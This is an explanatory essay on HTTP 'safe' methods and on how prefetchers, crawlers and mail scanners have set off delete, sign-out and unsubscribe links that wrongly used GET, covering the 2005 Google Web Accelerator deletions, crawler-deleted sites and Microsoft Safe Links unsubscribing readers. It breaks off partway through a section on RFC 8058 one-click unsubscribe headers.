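# Are read-only web requests safe? Prefetching incidents and AI retrieval tools

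## What HTTP means by a safe request

The Hypertext Transfer Protocol (HTTP) is the set of rules for how programs request web pages and how servers respond. The program making the request, usually a browser, is called the client. Every request starts with a method, a word that indicates the purpose of the request. The two most common methods are GET, which requests a resource such as a page, and POST, which submits data for the server to process. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022), the current standard for what the methods mean, notes that GET was the only method when the web began in 1990. Engineers mostly call this standard RFC 9110, after its number in the Requests for Comments, the series in which the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) publishes internet standards.

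A GET request is supposed to be read-only, meaning that the client receives a copy of something and the server's data don't change. Much software relies on this. Browsers fetch pages before anyone clicks, search engines follow the links they find, mail scanners open links to look for malware, and language models with web tools open pages, usually with no person approving the individual request. But some sites change data in response to a GET, so a program designed only to read can end up deleting a page or confirming a subscription.

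### Two requests, line by line

Suppose someone has logged in to a wiki and opens its page about a harbour. The browser sends roughly this:

```
GET /page?title=Harbour&do=show HTTP/1.1
Host: wiki.example.org
Cookie: session=7f3a9c
```

The first line holds the method, then the address within the site, then the protocol version. The part of the address after the question mark is the query string, which carries parameters to the server, here `title` and `do`. The Host line names the site, since one machine may serve many sites.

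The Cookie line identifies the user's login session. HTTP is stateless, meaning that a server can handle each request without any record of earlier ones, so HTTP alone would not keep anyone logged in. A cookie is a small piece of data that the server sends to the browser and the browser returns with later requests. This allows what *Cookies* (Bingler, West and Wilander, 2025) calls a "stateful session" over a mostly stateless protocol. In the example, the server issued the value `7f3a9c` at login and linked it to one person's account, so it treats any request with that value as that person's. The cookie doesn't show whether the person clicked a link or the browser sent the request unprompted.

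Now the same person fills in a form to delete the page, and presses the button:

```
POST /page?title=Harbour HTTP/1.1
Host: wiki.example.org
Cookie: session=7f3a9c
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded
Content-Length: 26

do=delete&reason=duplicate
```

The blank line ends the headers, and the body after it holds the contents of the form. A GET normally has no body. RFC 9110 defines no general meaning for content in a GET and advises clients not to send any, so the input to a GET has to go in the address.

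The server acts on whichever of these parts its programmer chose to read. The program behind the address receives the method, the path, the query string, the cookie and the body as so many strings of text. A careful programmer checks that the method is POST before deleting anything. A careless one looks for `do=delete` wherever it turns up, and on that wiki the following line, with the cookie attached, removes the page just as well as the form does:

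```
GET /page?title=Harbour&do=delete HTTP/1.1
```

Hyperlinks generally send GET requests, whereas a developer can choose GET or POST for a form, as Jacobs (2004) explains in *URIs, Addressability, and the use of HTTP GET and POST*, a guideline from the Technical Architecture Group of the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C). A developer who wants a "delete" link beside each entry, without a form or button, therefore tends to create an action link, which makes the server perform an action as soon as any program fetches it.

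### Safe and idempotent

RFC 9110 has a name for methods that should never work like this. A method is safe if its meaning is "essentially read-only", which Fielding and colleagues spell out as follows: "the client does not request, and does not expect, any state change". A state change is a lasting change in what the server stores. They add that reasonable use of a safe method should not cause harm, loss of property or an unusual burden on the server. GET is safe, and so is HEAD, which asks for the headers of a page without its content. (OPTIONS and TRACE, two diagnostic methods, are safe as well.)

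Idempotence is a weaker property than safety. A request is idempotent if its intended effect is the same whether the client sends it once or many times. Let *s* be what the server stores and *r*(*s*) what it should store after request *r*, counting only the effects that the client asked for. Then *r* is safe if *r*(*s*) = *s*, and idempotent if *r*(*r*(*s*)) = *r*(*s*). The second equation follows from the first, so every safe request is idempotent. The reverse is not true, and the standard counterexample is the DELETE method. The first DELETE removes the page, so the method is not safe. A second has nothing to remove and may well get an error message in reply, but it leaves the server in the same state, so the method is idempotent.

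MDN's *HTTP request methods*, from the reference site that Mozilla runs for web developers, classes the common methods like this:

| Method | What the client asks for | Safe | Idempotent | Cacheable |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GET | a copy of the resource | yes | yes | yes |
| HEAD | the headers only | yes | yes | yes |
| PUT | replace the resource with this content | no | yes | no |
| DELETE | remove the resource | no | yes | no |
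| POST | process this content | no | no | under conditions |

People have confused safety with idempotence from early on. In 1999, Connolly, then at the W3C, remarked that what people now called "safe" had previously been wrongly called "idempotent". An unsubscribe link breaks the rule for GET, because the first fetch takes someone off the list. Its developer may still think it complies, because five clicks have the same effect as one.

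### From "should never" to "MUST"

The rule is about as old as HTTP. The HTTP/1.0 specification, RFC 1945, included it in the security considerations: GET and HEAD "should never have the significance of taking an action other than retrieval". RFC 2068, the first standard for HTTP/1.1, which the IETF published in 1997, has the same words and differs mainly in placing them in the definitions of the methods. *Safe Methods*, in Connected: An Internet Encyclopedia, reproduces the passage.

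Some developers ignored the rule even then. On the HTTP working group's mailing list in September 1996, Mike Meyer wrote that he routinely built applications with GETs that were not idempotent, provided he had a "captive audience". Fielding (1996), an editor of the standard, replied that Meyer was violating the protocol and betting that no misunderstanding would occur inside his controlled environment, and that he was personally responsible for any resulting loss of property. He added that the passage on safe methods sounds like legalese "precisely because it is legalese".

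The formal wording was weaker in the next version, though. *Hypertext Transfer Protocol* (Fielding et al., 1999), published as RFC 2616, replaced RFC 2068 and changed "should never" to "SHOULD NOT". The capitals show that the term has the meaning set for all standards in *RFC Key Words* (Bradner, 1997). Unlike "MUST NOT", which is an absolute prohibition, "SHOULD NOT" allows that there may be valid reasons, in particular circumstances, for which the behaviour is "acceptable or even useful", provided the implementer first understands the full implications and weighs the case.

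In June 2002 a contributor to the mailing list of Zope, a web application server, conceded in *RFC 2616, side effects, and idempotence* that the standard had no MUST on this point, so Zope did not violate it. The same message argued that "safe" was a separate property that deserved attention. In May 2005, after Google Web Accelerator had begun to preload the "delete this" links in people's web applications, some people cited RFC 2616 against the developers. Willison (2005), in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs*, answered them by citing Bradner's definition. On the wording alone both sides had a point, since a developer with a good reason could put an action behind a GET and still conform. But Bradner also required developers to weigh the implications, and it is harder to see how a public site could have met that condition. One implication was that browsers and crawlers would treat the link as harmless,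 and RFC 2616 itself gave developers notice of that convention.

RFC 9110 closes the gap for the case that had caused the trouble. Its example is web-based editing software with addresses such as `page?do=delete`. If the purpose of such an address is an unsafe action, the site's owner "MUST disable or disallow that action" for any request with a safe method. Otherwise, automated programs that send a GET to every address they find will cause "unfortunate side effects". A wiki that deletes pages on a GET now violates the standard, and special circumstances don't excuse it.

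### Who answers for an effect nobody requested

RFC 9110 defines safety by what the client asks for, not what the server does. A GET still counts as a safe request even though the server may respond with behaviour that is not entirely read-only, or even harmful. The client can't be held accountable for that behaviour because it didn't ask for it.

The HTTP specification gives two examples of permitted side effects. Most servers log every request, and a request still counts as safe even if the log eventually fills the disk and brings the server down. Following an advertisement also often leads to a charge on the advertiser's account, though the reader asked only for a page. Jacobs gives a milder example, a visitor counter that goes up by one with each view.

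Jacobs draws the line slightly differently, and his test is perhaps easier to apply. He asks whether the user has taken on an obligation. He compares a GET to a question and a POST to an order, and says nobody should incur an obligation by following a link. A notice such as "by following this link you agree to our terms" fails on this view, since anyone can link to the same page, and a visitor who arrives that way will never have seen the terms. Jacobs also describes a mailing list that asks new subscribers to confirm by email. In the correct design, the link in the email opens a page with a "Confirm" button that sends a POST. In the faulty design, opening the link confirms the subscription. If the reader's mail program then fetches links in advance to save time, the reader joins the list without knowing it, and Jacobs blames the server.

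A site can comply without giving up its links. *Forbid HTTP GET To Perform Non-Queries* recommends checking the method and, if a request for an action arrives by anything other than POST, answering with a filled-in form that asks the user to confirm. The developers of Trac, a wiki and bug tracker for software projects, adopted a similar policy. Every request that creates, modifies or deletes something has to use POST, and the server asks for confirmation before it deletes a page. Trac previously used a JavaScript dialog for this, which appears only when a person clicks in a browser that runs the script. A program that reads the address out of the page and fetches it never triggers the dialog, which is how the accelerator of 2005 got past the prompts that Willison mentions.

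The rule on accountability has two limits. It settles who is to blame but does not restore a deleted page, and it covers only effects that the client did not request. A crawler that follows a `do=delete` link without knowing what it does is not to blame for the deletion. Someone who sends the same GET request in order to delete the page has requested the deletion in any ordinary sense of the word, and it would be strange to read RFC 9110 as excusing them because they used GET.

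### Why nothing enforces the rule

The client labels its request with a method, but what happens next depends on server code that the client cannot see. HTTP hides that code by design, because the same interface has to work for a folder of files, a database or a gateway to an older system. As Fielding and colleagues put it, the protocol "cannot be defined in terms of what occurs behind the interface". HTTP has no response field in which a server must declare that a GET changed something. The IETF publishes standards but does not inspect websites, so researchers have had to estimate how many sites break the rule.

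In 1998 the IETF published an experimental response header, Safe, which let a server mark a request as harmless to repeat, chiefly so that browsers could handle retries of harmless POST requests more gracefully. Masinter, a co-author of RFC 2616, recalled in 2002 that the working group had regarded the server, not the method, as the final arbiter of safety, and that in most of the cases it looked at, a client needed to know only after the fact. That is enough when a reader presses "reload", but a program deciding whether to fetch a link has no response yet and can go only by the method. Fielding had objected in 1996 that notice in the response "would be too late", because the client must know before it sends the request.

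Software trusts it anyway, because the gains are large. Caching is one. A cache is a store of earlier responses, in the browser or on a machine between browser and server, and it can answer a repeated GET without troubling the server at all. RFC 9110 has caching rules for POST too, but the overwhelming majority of caches support only GET and HEAD. (This also means that an action link can fail in the opposite direction: if a cache supplies the page, the request never reaches the server and the action never takes place.)

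Whether a client can safely retry a request depends on idempotence. When a connection drops before the response arrives, the client cannot tell whether the server carried out the request. It can resend a GET or a DELETE, but resending a POST might place a second order. Fielding and colleagues therefore advise clients not to retry a POST automatically unless they have some way of knowing that repetition is harmless. They forbid proxies, which pass requests along on a client's behalf, from automatically retrying a POST at all.

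Crawling and prefetching depend on safety in the strict sense. According to RFC 9110, HTTP distinguishes safe methods from unsafe ones so that search engines can follow links and browsers can fetch pages ahead of the user "without fear of causing harm". A crawler cannot ask the owner of each link what it does, and prefetching would have little point if the browser had to ask the user first. Safe requests also help site owners get their content into search results. According to http.dev's *HTTP Methods*, content behind a POST needs an equivalent address that answers a plain GET before it can appear there.

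### QUERY, a safe method with a body

For most of the web's history, developers could also assume that a request with a body probably writes something, though this was never reliable because many sites use POST for searches. The filters for a complicated search can make an address too long, and filters in an address end up in the server's access logs, where private details may not belong. A POST avoids both problems, but caches and clients cannot tell a search by POST from a purchase, so caches skip the response and clients cannot safely retry the request.

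In June 2026 the IETF published a method for this case. Reschke, Snell and Bishop (2026), in *The HTTP QUERY Method*, or RFC 10008, define QUERY as a request that the server process the enclosed content "in a safe and idempotent manner" and return the result. According to IETF's *The HTTP QUERY Method* (2025), a late draft of the standard, the input travels in the body, as it does with POST. A search on the wiki from the earlier examples might look like this:

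```
QUERY /search HTTP/1.1
Host: wiki.example.org
Cookie: session=7f3a9c
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded
Content-Length: 24

text=harbour&sort=newest
```

A QUERY request could be a POST apart from its first word, which states that the client wants an answer and no change. InfoQ (2026) reports that QUERY is the first new standard method since PATCH in 2010, but Jacobs mentions that an IETF meeting had already discussed a "safe POST" in December 1996, without reaching consensus.

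QUERY lets a client send a large, structured question using a safe method, which GET never did well. However, it adds no enforcement. A programmer who lets a QUERY request delete a page violates the standard, but the client gets no more warning than it would with GET.

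## Google Web Accelerator and the deletions of 2005

In May 2005 Google released Google Web Accelerator, a program that sped up browsing partly by prefetching pages the user had not yet asked for. It relied on GET requests being safe inside people's private accounts, where many developers had assumed that only humans would click links. Two days after the release, 37signals, a Chicago software company, warned other developers that the program was triggering "delete" links in its customers' accounts.

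### The program and its choice of links

Google released the beta, or public test version, on 4 May for Windows users in North America and Europe, with support for Internet Explorer and Firefox. According to the launch text, which Tabke posted on the WebmasterWorld forum in *Google Windows Web Accelerator* (2005), the accelerator appeared in the browser as a small speedometer with a running total of the time saved.

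Part of the program ran on the user's computer and part on Google's servers. Tao of Mac's technical notes, *Google/Web Accelerator*, describe the local part as a proxy. Google's servers could answer the proxy's requests from their own store of pages or fetch the pages from the websites. Pages on HTTPS, the encrypted form of HTTP, did not go through Google. The blog post *Google Web Accelerator* (2005) pointed out that Google's privacy policy disclosed that the company temporarily stored the cookies that users' unencrypted requests carried to other sites.

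Even the people testing the program were unsure how it chose which links to prefetch. Google's help page told site owners how to mark a link for prefetching, and several readers concluded that the program prefetched only marked links. But when Tabke moved the mouse over an unmarked link, the program fetched the page about nine times out of ten. The exceptions seemed to be links in small type and CGI addresses, where a script builds the page on request. David Heinemeier Hansson, who created the web framework Ruby on Rails and worked on 37signals' products, wrote that the program followed every ordinary link outside HTTPS. Another commenter put up a page of links, visited it with the accelerator running and found no prefetches in the server's log.

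Much of this makes sense in light of a rule that Marissa Mayer, Google's director of consumer web products, described to the trade publication eWeek. The accelerator ignored links with a question mark in the address, as Hicks (2005), in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security*, reported. Mayer's reasoning was that a query string usually carries something like a user ID, and that a link which deletes something would typically have one. (One tester did report that the program fetched addresses with query strings as well.)

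Under that rule, the accelerator would have skipped an address like `page?do=delete`. But some developers had rewritten their addresses to make them tidier. A commenter in Slashdot's *Google Accelerator* (2005) pointed out that the 37signals products Basecamp and Backpack apparently used the form `/account/delete/121` rather than `/account?action=delete&id=121`. A server can treat the two as the same instruction, but the accelerator would skip the second and might fetch the first.

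### One deletion, step by step

Take the wiki from the previous section again, and suppose that its addresses have no question marks. A logged-in user opens the page about the harbour, which has a "Delete" link in one corner. In the page's code the link looks like this:

```
<a href="/page/harbour/delete"
   onclick="return confirm('Delete this page?')">Delete</a>
```

The accelerator takes the address from the `href` part, perhaps because the user's mouse crossed the link on its way to something else. The wiki's server then receives roughly this:

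```
GET /page/harbour/delete HTTP/1.1
Host: wiki.example.org
Cookie: session=7f3a9c
X-moz: prefetch
```

The server looks up the session, finds that the user is allowed to delete pages, and deletes the page. The accelerator caches the server's reply, presumably a notice that the page is gone, so that it can appear quickly if the user ever clicks the link. The user sees no change on the screen.

The JavaScript confirmation in `onclick` can stop the request if the user chooses "Cancel", but like the dialog that Trac once used, it runs only on a click, and here nobody clicked. One commenter under the 37signals warning wondered whether the accelerator was answering "yes" for the user, and another explained that it ignored the script. The server can't tell that the confirmation was skipped by checking for the user's answer, because the browser never sends that answer.

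The cookie explains why developers had not run into this more often. *google web accelerator vs rails*, a blog post of 6 May 2005, observed that search crawlers and caching servers had never exposed the flaw because they weren't logged in. Crawlers couldn't see "Delete" links that appeared only after login, and many developers had come to regard the login as sufficient protection. The accelerator, however, fetched pages as the logged-in user.

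Deletion was the worst case, but prefetching by the accelerator could trigger any link that performed an action. Mike Rumble, a web programmer in Britain, told Hicks that he could no longer use his webmail because every click led back to the sign-in page. He concluded that the accelerator was fetching the "sign out" link as soon as he signed in.

### What users lost and what they feared

The main evidence of lost data is *Google Web Accelerator* (2005), the warning that 37signals published on its company blog, Signal v. Noise, on 6 May. The day before, "a few people" had reported that their pages in Backpack, which had launched that week, were "disappearing". The developers could not explain the problem until they looked into the accelerator's behaviour. They then added code to refuse its prefetches. Jason Fried, the company's president, told Hicks that the block was in place within 30 minutes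 of the diagnosis.

Hicks describes the damage slightly differently, reporting that a few users of Basecamp and Backpack complained about deleted accounts. Losing whole accounts would be far worse than losing pages, and nothing in the blog post supports it, so it is safer to assume that users lost pages. Neither report gives a number or mentions whether 37signals recovered the data.

Deletions outside 37signals are less well documented. One commenter on the warning wrote that the accelerator had deleted "some of our very important leads" from a company database that morning. Another had seen a forum thread in which nearly half the comments were labeled "deleted by the user", and apparently suspected the accelerator, but had no evidence beyond the timing.

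The remaining complaints were about damage that could happen. In *Google's Accelerator in need of a recall*, Heinemeier Hansson demanded that Google withdraw the program and wrote of "death and destruction", though at a much lower level of criticality than a faulty car. In the discussion below the post, he added that phpMyAdmin, a browser-based database tool, could instantly wipe a user's databases, and that Google's own Blogger could wipe all of a user's comments. A commenter at Signal v. Noise ran the accelerator on a test copy of phpMyAdmin and lost nothing. The commenter's own administration pages, which had "delete" links that used GET, also survived. Google's question-mark rule may be the reason. Another sceptic went through 134 comments and counted only a few from people who claimed to have seen the behaviour themselves.

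37signals traced the loss of Backpack users' pages to the prefetching, but one commenter suggested that strangers had seen those pages by mistake and clicked "Delete". Google confirmed that on as many as five sites the accelerator was showing people cached pages with somebody else's user name on them. The commenter's explanation is unlikely because, by Mayer's account, a stranger who saw such a page did not have the other person's session cookie. Clicking an ordinary "Delete" link would therefore have sent the stranger's own cookie to the server.

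The documented losses are some pages belonging to a few customers of one company, plus one firm's sales leads. But the program was two days old when the warning appeared, and it soon became hard to obtain, so the small losses are weak evidence of how much damage it would have done with many users.

Mayer first told Hicks that most of the reports she had seen looked unsubstantiated. When she heard about 37signals, she replied that some sites might not be complying with the standard. She also conceded that Google's assumption about the question mark could be wrong, in which case the company would have to redesign how the program chose links. By 7 May Google's download page carried a notice that the accelerator had reached its "maximum capacity of users". A commenter at Signal v. Noise suspected that this was a polite way of withdrawing the program. That is plausible, but Google did not give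 that reason.

### The block by request header

37signals recommended checking requests for the header in the last line of the example, `X-moz: prefetch`. The header came from Mozilla, whose Firefox browser could also prefetch pages. A server that receives it can return the status code 403, "Forbidden", without running the code that deletes anything. Site owners already had such rules. On 1 April 2005, a month before the accelerator came out, a member of WebmasterWorld (2005) posted one to block prefetching by Firefox.

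The block was quick to install but easy to get wrong. One version that circulated in the comments at Signal v. Noise converted the header's value to uppercase and then compared it with "prefetch" in lowercase. The two could never match, so a site that copied the code had no protection, and its owner would not have noticed until something disappeared. A rule that refused every prefetch also refused harmless ones, such as those for images.

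A more basic weakness was that the method relied on programs to identify themselves. Another commenter pointed out that the download tool Wget can follow every link on a site with a user's cookies and sends no such header. The accelerator itself may not always have sent it either. Tao of Mac, while recommending the 403, noted the header only in requests for pages that the site's owner had designated for prefetching. If that was generally true, the rule would have missed the ordinary "Delete" links it was meant for.

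The accelerator returned in October 2005, and developers soon claimed that the block no longer worked. Andrews (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator*, a message to a mailing list for developers of the blogging software WordPress, wrote that the new version did not identify itself in the header. Bicking (2005), in *Google at it again*, made the same claim but qualified it with "apparently". Neither described a test, and the two reports may well go back to a single source, since Andrews linked to a new post by 37signals. Google's help page suggests that later versions, at least, did send the header. According to WebmasterWorld (2008), the page still told site owners in July 2008 that they could refuse prefetches by returning a 403 to requests with this header. The member who quoted the advice added that he wasn't suggesting it worked.

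Google's help page now stated the question-mark rule, and Deaton (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator*, quoted it to the WordPress list. Google cited the HTTP standard, then added that "in practice" the program skipped addresses with a question mark and pages on HTTPS. Bainbridge, in *Google Web Accelerator*, concluded that the list's worry about links such as `index.php?action=delete&id=123` was unfounded. Bicking conceded that this version seemed somewhat improved, although Mayer had described the same rule in May. The rule still left addresses without a question mark, like those of Backpack, exposed to prefetching. Google issued the last version in January 2008 and discontinued the program that October.

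### Who was to blame

Within hours of the warning, commenters were quoting to 37signals the "SHOULD NOT" in RFC 2616, the HTTP standard at the time. Mark Nottingham, later a co-author of RFC 9110, told the company in the comments on Signal v. Noise that a properly designed web application would have no problem with the accelerator. Fried acknowledged to Hicks that a deletion should technically use a button, not a link.

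The exception that Willison had in mind when he defended the developers on that wording was the login, which he called "a perfectly acceptable compromise". Heinemeier Hansson used the same defence. But Willison dropped most of it the same day, because his readers had shown him that a login offers little protection even if nobody prefetches anything. A hostile website can include an image whose address is really the "Delete" link of another site. A visitor's browser requests the supposed image and attaches the visitor's cookie, and the other site deletes the page. This attack is called cross-site request forgery. Willison still thought that the standard covered people who had considered a dangerous GET long and hard, but he now wrote that anyone who had overlooked forgery and caching proxies hadn't been "thinking hard enough". (A further update admitted that switching to POST doesn't stop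 forgery either. A hostile page can submit a form.)

Shiflett (2006), in *Google Web Accelerator Debate*, used this to defend Google. For each kind of link that people complained about, he asked whether the accelerator would have fetched it and whether an attacker could have forged it. The usual protection against forgery is a token (`abcd` in his examples), a random string shared only between the server and one user's browser.

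| Link | Accelerator may fetch it | Open to forgery |
|---|---|---|
| `/delete.php?item=socks` | no | yes |
| `/delete.php` | yes | yes |
| `/delete.php?token=abcd` | no | no |
| `/delete/all/abcd` | yes | no |

Shiflett argued that only the last kind of link gives a developer a fair complaint against Google, because a site with such links was secure until the accelerator appeared, and he had never seen anyone cite one. This is a good answer to the claim that developers had weighed the implications, as the definition of "SHOULD NOT" required, because they had left their users' data open to deletion by any other website. It is less convincing as a defence of Google. Forgery requires an attacker who knows the site's addresses and wants to do harm, so a site with this flaw could run for years without losing a page, whereas the accelerator could trigger the links for anyone who installed it.

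The programmer Ian Bicking did not think the standard blamed the developers. In *GWA and RFC 2616*, he reproduced the whole passage, which is less one-sided than the quotations from it. Like the later RFC 9110, it absolves the user, who "did not request the side-effects", but it does not identify who is accountable instead. Bicking blamed Google for breaking people's expectations. In the comments at Signal v. Noise, Mark Baker called the dispute over "SHOULD" and "MUST" immaterial and argued that the user was acting through the accelerator, so could not be held accountable for a change made by a GET. The opening of the RFC 2616 passage supports this argument, since it describes software as representing the user. If the user is not accountable for a request, it is hard to see how the user's software could be at fault for it.

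But that opening sentence also gives the makers of such software a duty to take care that users know of any actions that may have "an unexpected significance to themselves or others". The accelerator had an option to mark links, but only after it had fetched them, which is too late to warn users of a deletion. Google could answer that the rest of the passage treats GET as the ordinary case and explains that a client meets this duty by presenting POST and other unsafe methods in a special way. Under the 2005 text, then, the developers were at fault and Google followed the rules.

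Whether Google acted prudently is a different matter. The same passage mentions that some sites treat side effects of a GET as "a feature", so it was clear from the standard itself that not every GET was safe. Google knew this too, since it would otherwise have had no reason to skip addresses with a question mark. It used the question mark to guess which links were unsafe, and the guess was wrong for sites like Backpack.

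Bicking's other argument, in *Breaking the Web We Have*, was that it didn't matter who had kept to the standard. Sites had worked before the accelerator and failed with it, so he blamed the accelerator. He later added that it behaved like a crawler while "pretending it's a user", and called this an unforeseen loophole in the standard. That is a fair description. Site owners relied on crawlers to visit without logging in and generally to follow robots.txt, the file in which a site lists the pages that crawlers should leave alone. One site owner on WebmasterWorld found no sign in his logs that the accelerator was checking robots.txt. Tabke replied to such complaints that the accelerator was a proxy acting for a human, not a bot. Site owners thus got automated requests that they could not block in the usual way.

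As a general rule, though, Bicking's principle would let any widespread bad practice limit what new software may do. Commenters reminded Heinemeier Hansson that ordinary crawlers had already triggered "revert" links in Instiki, an earlier wiki of his, because the links used GET. Even if Google had withdrawn its program for good on the first day, the next prefetcher or browser plug-in would have found the same links.

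Bicking attributed the bad practice to HTML, which he said made the correct design awkward. A POST needed a form, and HTML did not allow one form inside another. His example was a form for editing a list of addresses, with a "delete this address" link beside each one. A commenter answered that each link could be another submit button in the same form, with its own name so that the server could tell which one the user pressed. Bicking conceded that this was possible but thought it would be difficult to add to an old application. Others complained that buttons look heavy, and Shiflett responded by demonstrating a button styled to look exactly like a link.

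On 7 May Heinemeier Hansson, in *Google*, agreed that POST was a better way to modify data and reported that 37signals had switched Backpack to it the day before. The next version of Ruby on Rails would include a link that sent a POST using JavaScript, so that other developers could use POST as easily as GET. He still wanted Google to recall the accelerator. Backpack was new and its developers were available to change it, but many old web applications no longer had anyone to rewrite them. He complained again when the accelerator came back in October, and Tilkov (2005), in *GWA vs. RoR*, sided with the three bloggers who had explained why he was wrong.

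Some cases had no simple fix. Opening an email in a webmail program is a retrieval, but it also marks the message as read, so a prefetcher that opens the whole inbox leaves the user unable to tell which messages are new. Users don't want to press a form button to read each message. One of Bicking's readers replied that desktop mail programs copy messages to the user's computer without marking them as read, and asked why a web cache should be any different. That is sensible, but the webmail server would need some signal from the client to distinguish a prefetch from a person opening a message. Signing out was nearly as awkward, because almost every site used a plain link for it. A Slashdot commenter found it ironic that developers were being lectured about this on Slashdot, whose own "Logout" link used GET.

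### Mozilla's opt-in

Bicking and others contrasted the accelerator with Mozilla's prefetching, which left ordinary links alone. The author of a page had to name the next page explicitly, for example with this line:

```
<link rel="prefetch" href="/page/lighthouse">
```

According to Mozilla's published guidance, which commenters quoted at Signal v. Noise, its browser did not prefetch addresses with a query string or pages on HTTPS. Google had adopted the same two exclusions but not Mozilla's requirement that the page's author mark a link for prefetching. This requirement would have prevented the Backpack deletions, since no developer has a reason to mark a "Delete" link that way. Mozilla was more careful than the standard required, because the 2005 passage on safe methods did not call for such marking.

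Under the opt-in, prefetching saved no time on pages whose authors hadn't opted in. The gains from prefetching were uncertain anyway. Nottingham (2005), in *Prefetching (again)*, recalled that a company called CacheFlow had sold a prefetching cache in the late 1990s, and that the industry eventually decided that prefetching by ordinary proxies wasn't worth the overhead. He thought prefetching made more sense when a cache coordinated it with the publisher of the pages.

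Mozilla's version also let a browser prefetch pages from a site without its owner's permission. Only the owner of the page containing the link had to permit it, and the link could lead to someone else's site. Google's search results began using the feature in the spring of 2005, and Weinstein (2005) complained about it that June in *Google's new feature creates another user privacy problem*. A search in Firefox could now make the browser fetch a top result that the user had not chosen to visit. One Firefox user on WebmasterWorld objected that he would be visiting sites he did not want to visit and collecting their cookies.

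## Search crawlers and mail scanners that set off links

Unlike Google Web Accelerator, a search crawler has no session cookie, so on most sites it can reach only public pages. If a site's login check is faulty, the crawler can still delete the site's content by following its delete links. Software that scans email for malware can set off links without a cookie or a faulty login check, because a link in an email often works for anyone who opens it.

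### The Spider of Doom

The best-known crawler story is "The Spider of Doom", from The Daily WTF, a website that collects stories about programming mistakes. It was circulating by 30 March 2006, when the search-industry news site Search Engine Roundtable summarised what is evidently the same story in *GoogleBot Deletes All Of Webmasters Content; Site Owner's Fault* (2006).

In the story, a company builds a content management system for a fairly large government website, and the client's staff spend months moving their pages into it. Six days after the launch, all the content is gone. Josh Breckman, a programmer, traces the deletions to one outside address belonging to Googlebot, Google's crawler. Someone on the client's staff copied text from one page to another, along with an "edit" link. Googlebot followed that link into the editing pages, where it found links labelled "Delete Page" and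 followed those too.

The editing pages were supposed to require a login. According to the story, the system checked whether a cookie named `isLoggedOn` had the value "false". Googlebot didn't use cookies, so it had no such value and passed. The difference comes down to one comparison:

```
if (cookie.isLoggedOn == "false") refuse();   // lets Googlebot in
if (cookie.isLoggedOn != "true")  refuse();   // keeps Googlebot out
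```

Even the second version would stop only honest visitors, since anyone can set their own cookie to "true". A proper check looks up a session value on the server, as the wiki in the earlier examples does with `7f3a9c`.

The system also used JavaScript to send logged-out visitors to the login page, but Googlebot didn't run the script. A script like that runs only after the server has sent the page with all its links.

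Breckman restored a fairly old backup and explained the flaw to his managers. They did not fix it and told the client never to copy and paste content from other pages.

The account is anonymous, and nobody has named the website. The Daily WTF's *Story Submission Guidelines* call its stories "dramatized retellings" of actual events and warn that the editors make up names, so "Josh Breckman" is probably a made-up name. The site's *New Editorial Guidelines* add that the editors ask most submitters questions but exaggerate some parts for entertainment, so the details deserve little weight.

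There is better evidence that crawlers do this. In October 2005, a Google employee wrote on the blog ImperialViolet that Google's crawler had once wiped out "a kind of proto wiki" with a "Delete this page" link at the bottom of each page. The owner emailed Google to ask for his website back, and the employee believed Google had recovered the pages from its crawl data. This is probably a separate incident from Breckman's, since Breckman used a backup.

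The only case with a published log entry is a small one. QuimaxW (2009), in *Mythweb...beware the googlebot*, reported losing every television recording on a home server. The log showed a visitor that identified itself as Googlebot sending this request:

```
GET /mythweb/tv/recorded?delete=yes&chanid=2491&starttime=1232571600 HTTP/1.1
```

The accelerator would have skipped this address because it contained a question mark. The recorder's web pages had no login. Their owner had assumed nobody would find them, but had put the address in a public forum profile.

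### How a mail scanner unsubscribes a reader

A phishing email usually depends on a link, so mail security software checks where links lead. Microsoft's Safe Links service scans the links in a message before delivering it, and Microsoft recommends a setting that holds the message back until the scan is complete. If a link has no established reputation, the service "detonates" it, meaning it opens the link in an isolated environment to see what it does.

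Suppose that the harbour wiki sends out a newsletter with an "Unsubscribe" link at the bottom. The link contains a code, `8c41e7`, that identifies the subscriber. When the newsletter reaches the reader's employer, the scanner opens the link:

```
GET /unsubscribe/8c41e7 HTTP/1.1
Host: lists.example.org
```

The server looks up the code, removes the reader from the list and returns a confirmation page. The scanner finds nothing malicious on that page, so it lets the newsletter through to the reader, who has no reason to suspect that they have been unsubscribed. The request has no Cookie line because the code alone identifies the reader.

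*ATP Safe Links are automatically unsubscribing users from email lists* (Stockburger, 2018) describes this happening at an organisation that had turned on Safe Links a few weeks earlier, where Stockburger was an administrator. Between 500 and 1,000 of its users subscribed to a couple of the affected lists, and all of them lost their subscriptions the first time each list sent a message. He wasn't sure whether the cause was the scan or Safe Links rewriting links to pass through Microsoft. The scan is much more likely, since rewriting a link doesn't by itself send a request to the list's server.

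Someone replied to Stockburger with the passage on safe methods from RFC 2616 and told him to complain to the lists. He accepted that Microsoft wasn't at fault, but many of the lists were old academic ones that nobody had kept up to date. One list host removed the link from messages to his organisation, and another told him it couldn't. Some of his users resubscribed with their personal addresses.

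A scanner can set off more than unsubscribe links. *Possible major problem with MS Defender scanning/clicking links* describes an organisation that emailed staff "Approve" and "Reject" links for internal requests. An administrator there reported that requests were being approved as soon as the email arrived. "Approve" was the first link, and when the administrator swapped the two, the requests were rejected instead. The administrator suspected Microsoft's scanner but hadn't proved it, though the swap does show that something was opening the first link regardless of its label.

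The security company Sophos warns that Microsoft's mail scanner can release suspicious messages that Sophos's own filter has quarantined. The filter sends users a summary of these messages with links to release them, and Microsoft's scanner can open those links. Sophos advises customers to exempt its domain from the scan. An administrator has to set up the exemption at each organisation, so this approach is of little use to a newsletter with readers at thousands of them.

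### One-click unsubscribing by POST

The obvious fix is the one Jacobs recommended for mailing lists, where the link opens a page and the reader presses a button there to unsubscribe. Many senders adopted it, but *Signaling One-Click Functionality for List Email Headers* (Levine and Herkula, 2017), the standard also known as RFC 8058, describes two drawbacks. Readers who find it hard to unsubscribe report the newsletter as junk instead, and enough such reports can send it to everyone's junk folder. A mail service may also want to unsubscribe someone automatically, for example when they report a message as junk or abandon their mailbox, and then nobody is there to press the button.

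RFC 8058 solves this with two lines in the headers of the email, which mail programs read but usually don't display:

```
List-Unsubscribe: <https://lists.example.org/unsubscribe/8c41e7>
List-Unsubscribe-Post: List-Unsubscribe=One-Click
```

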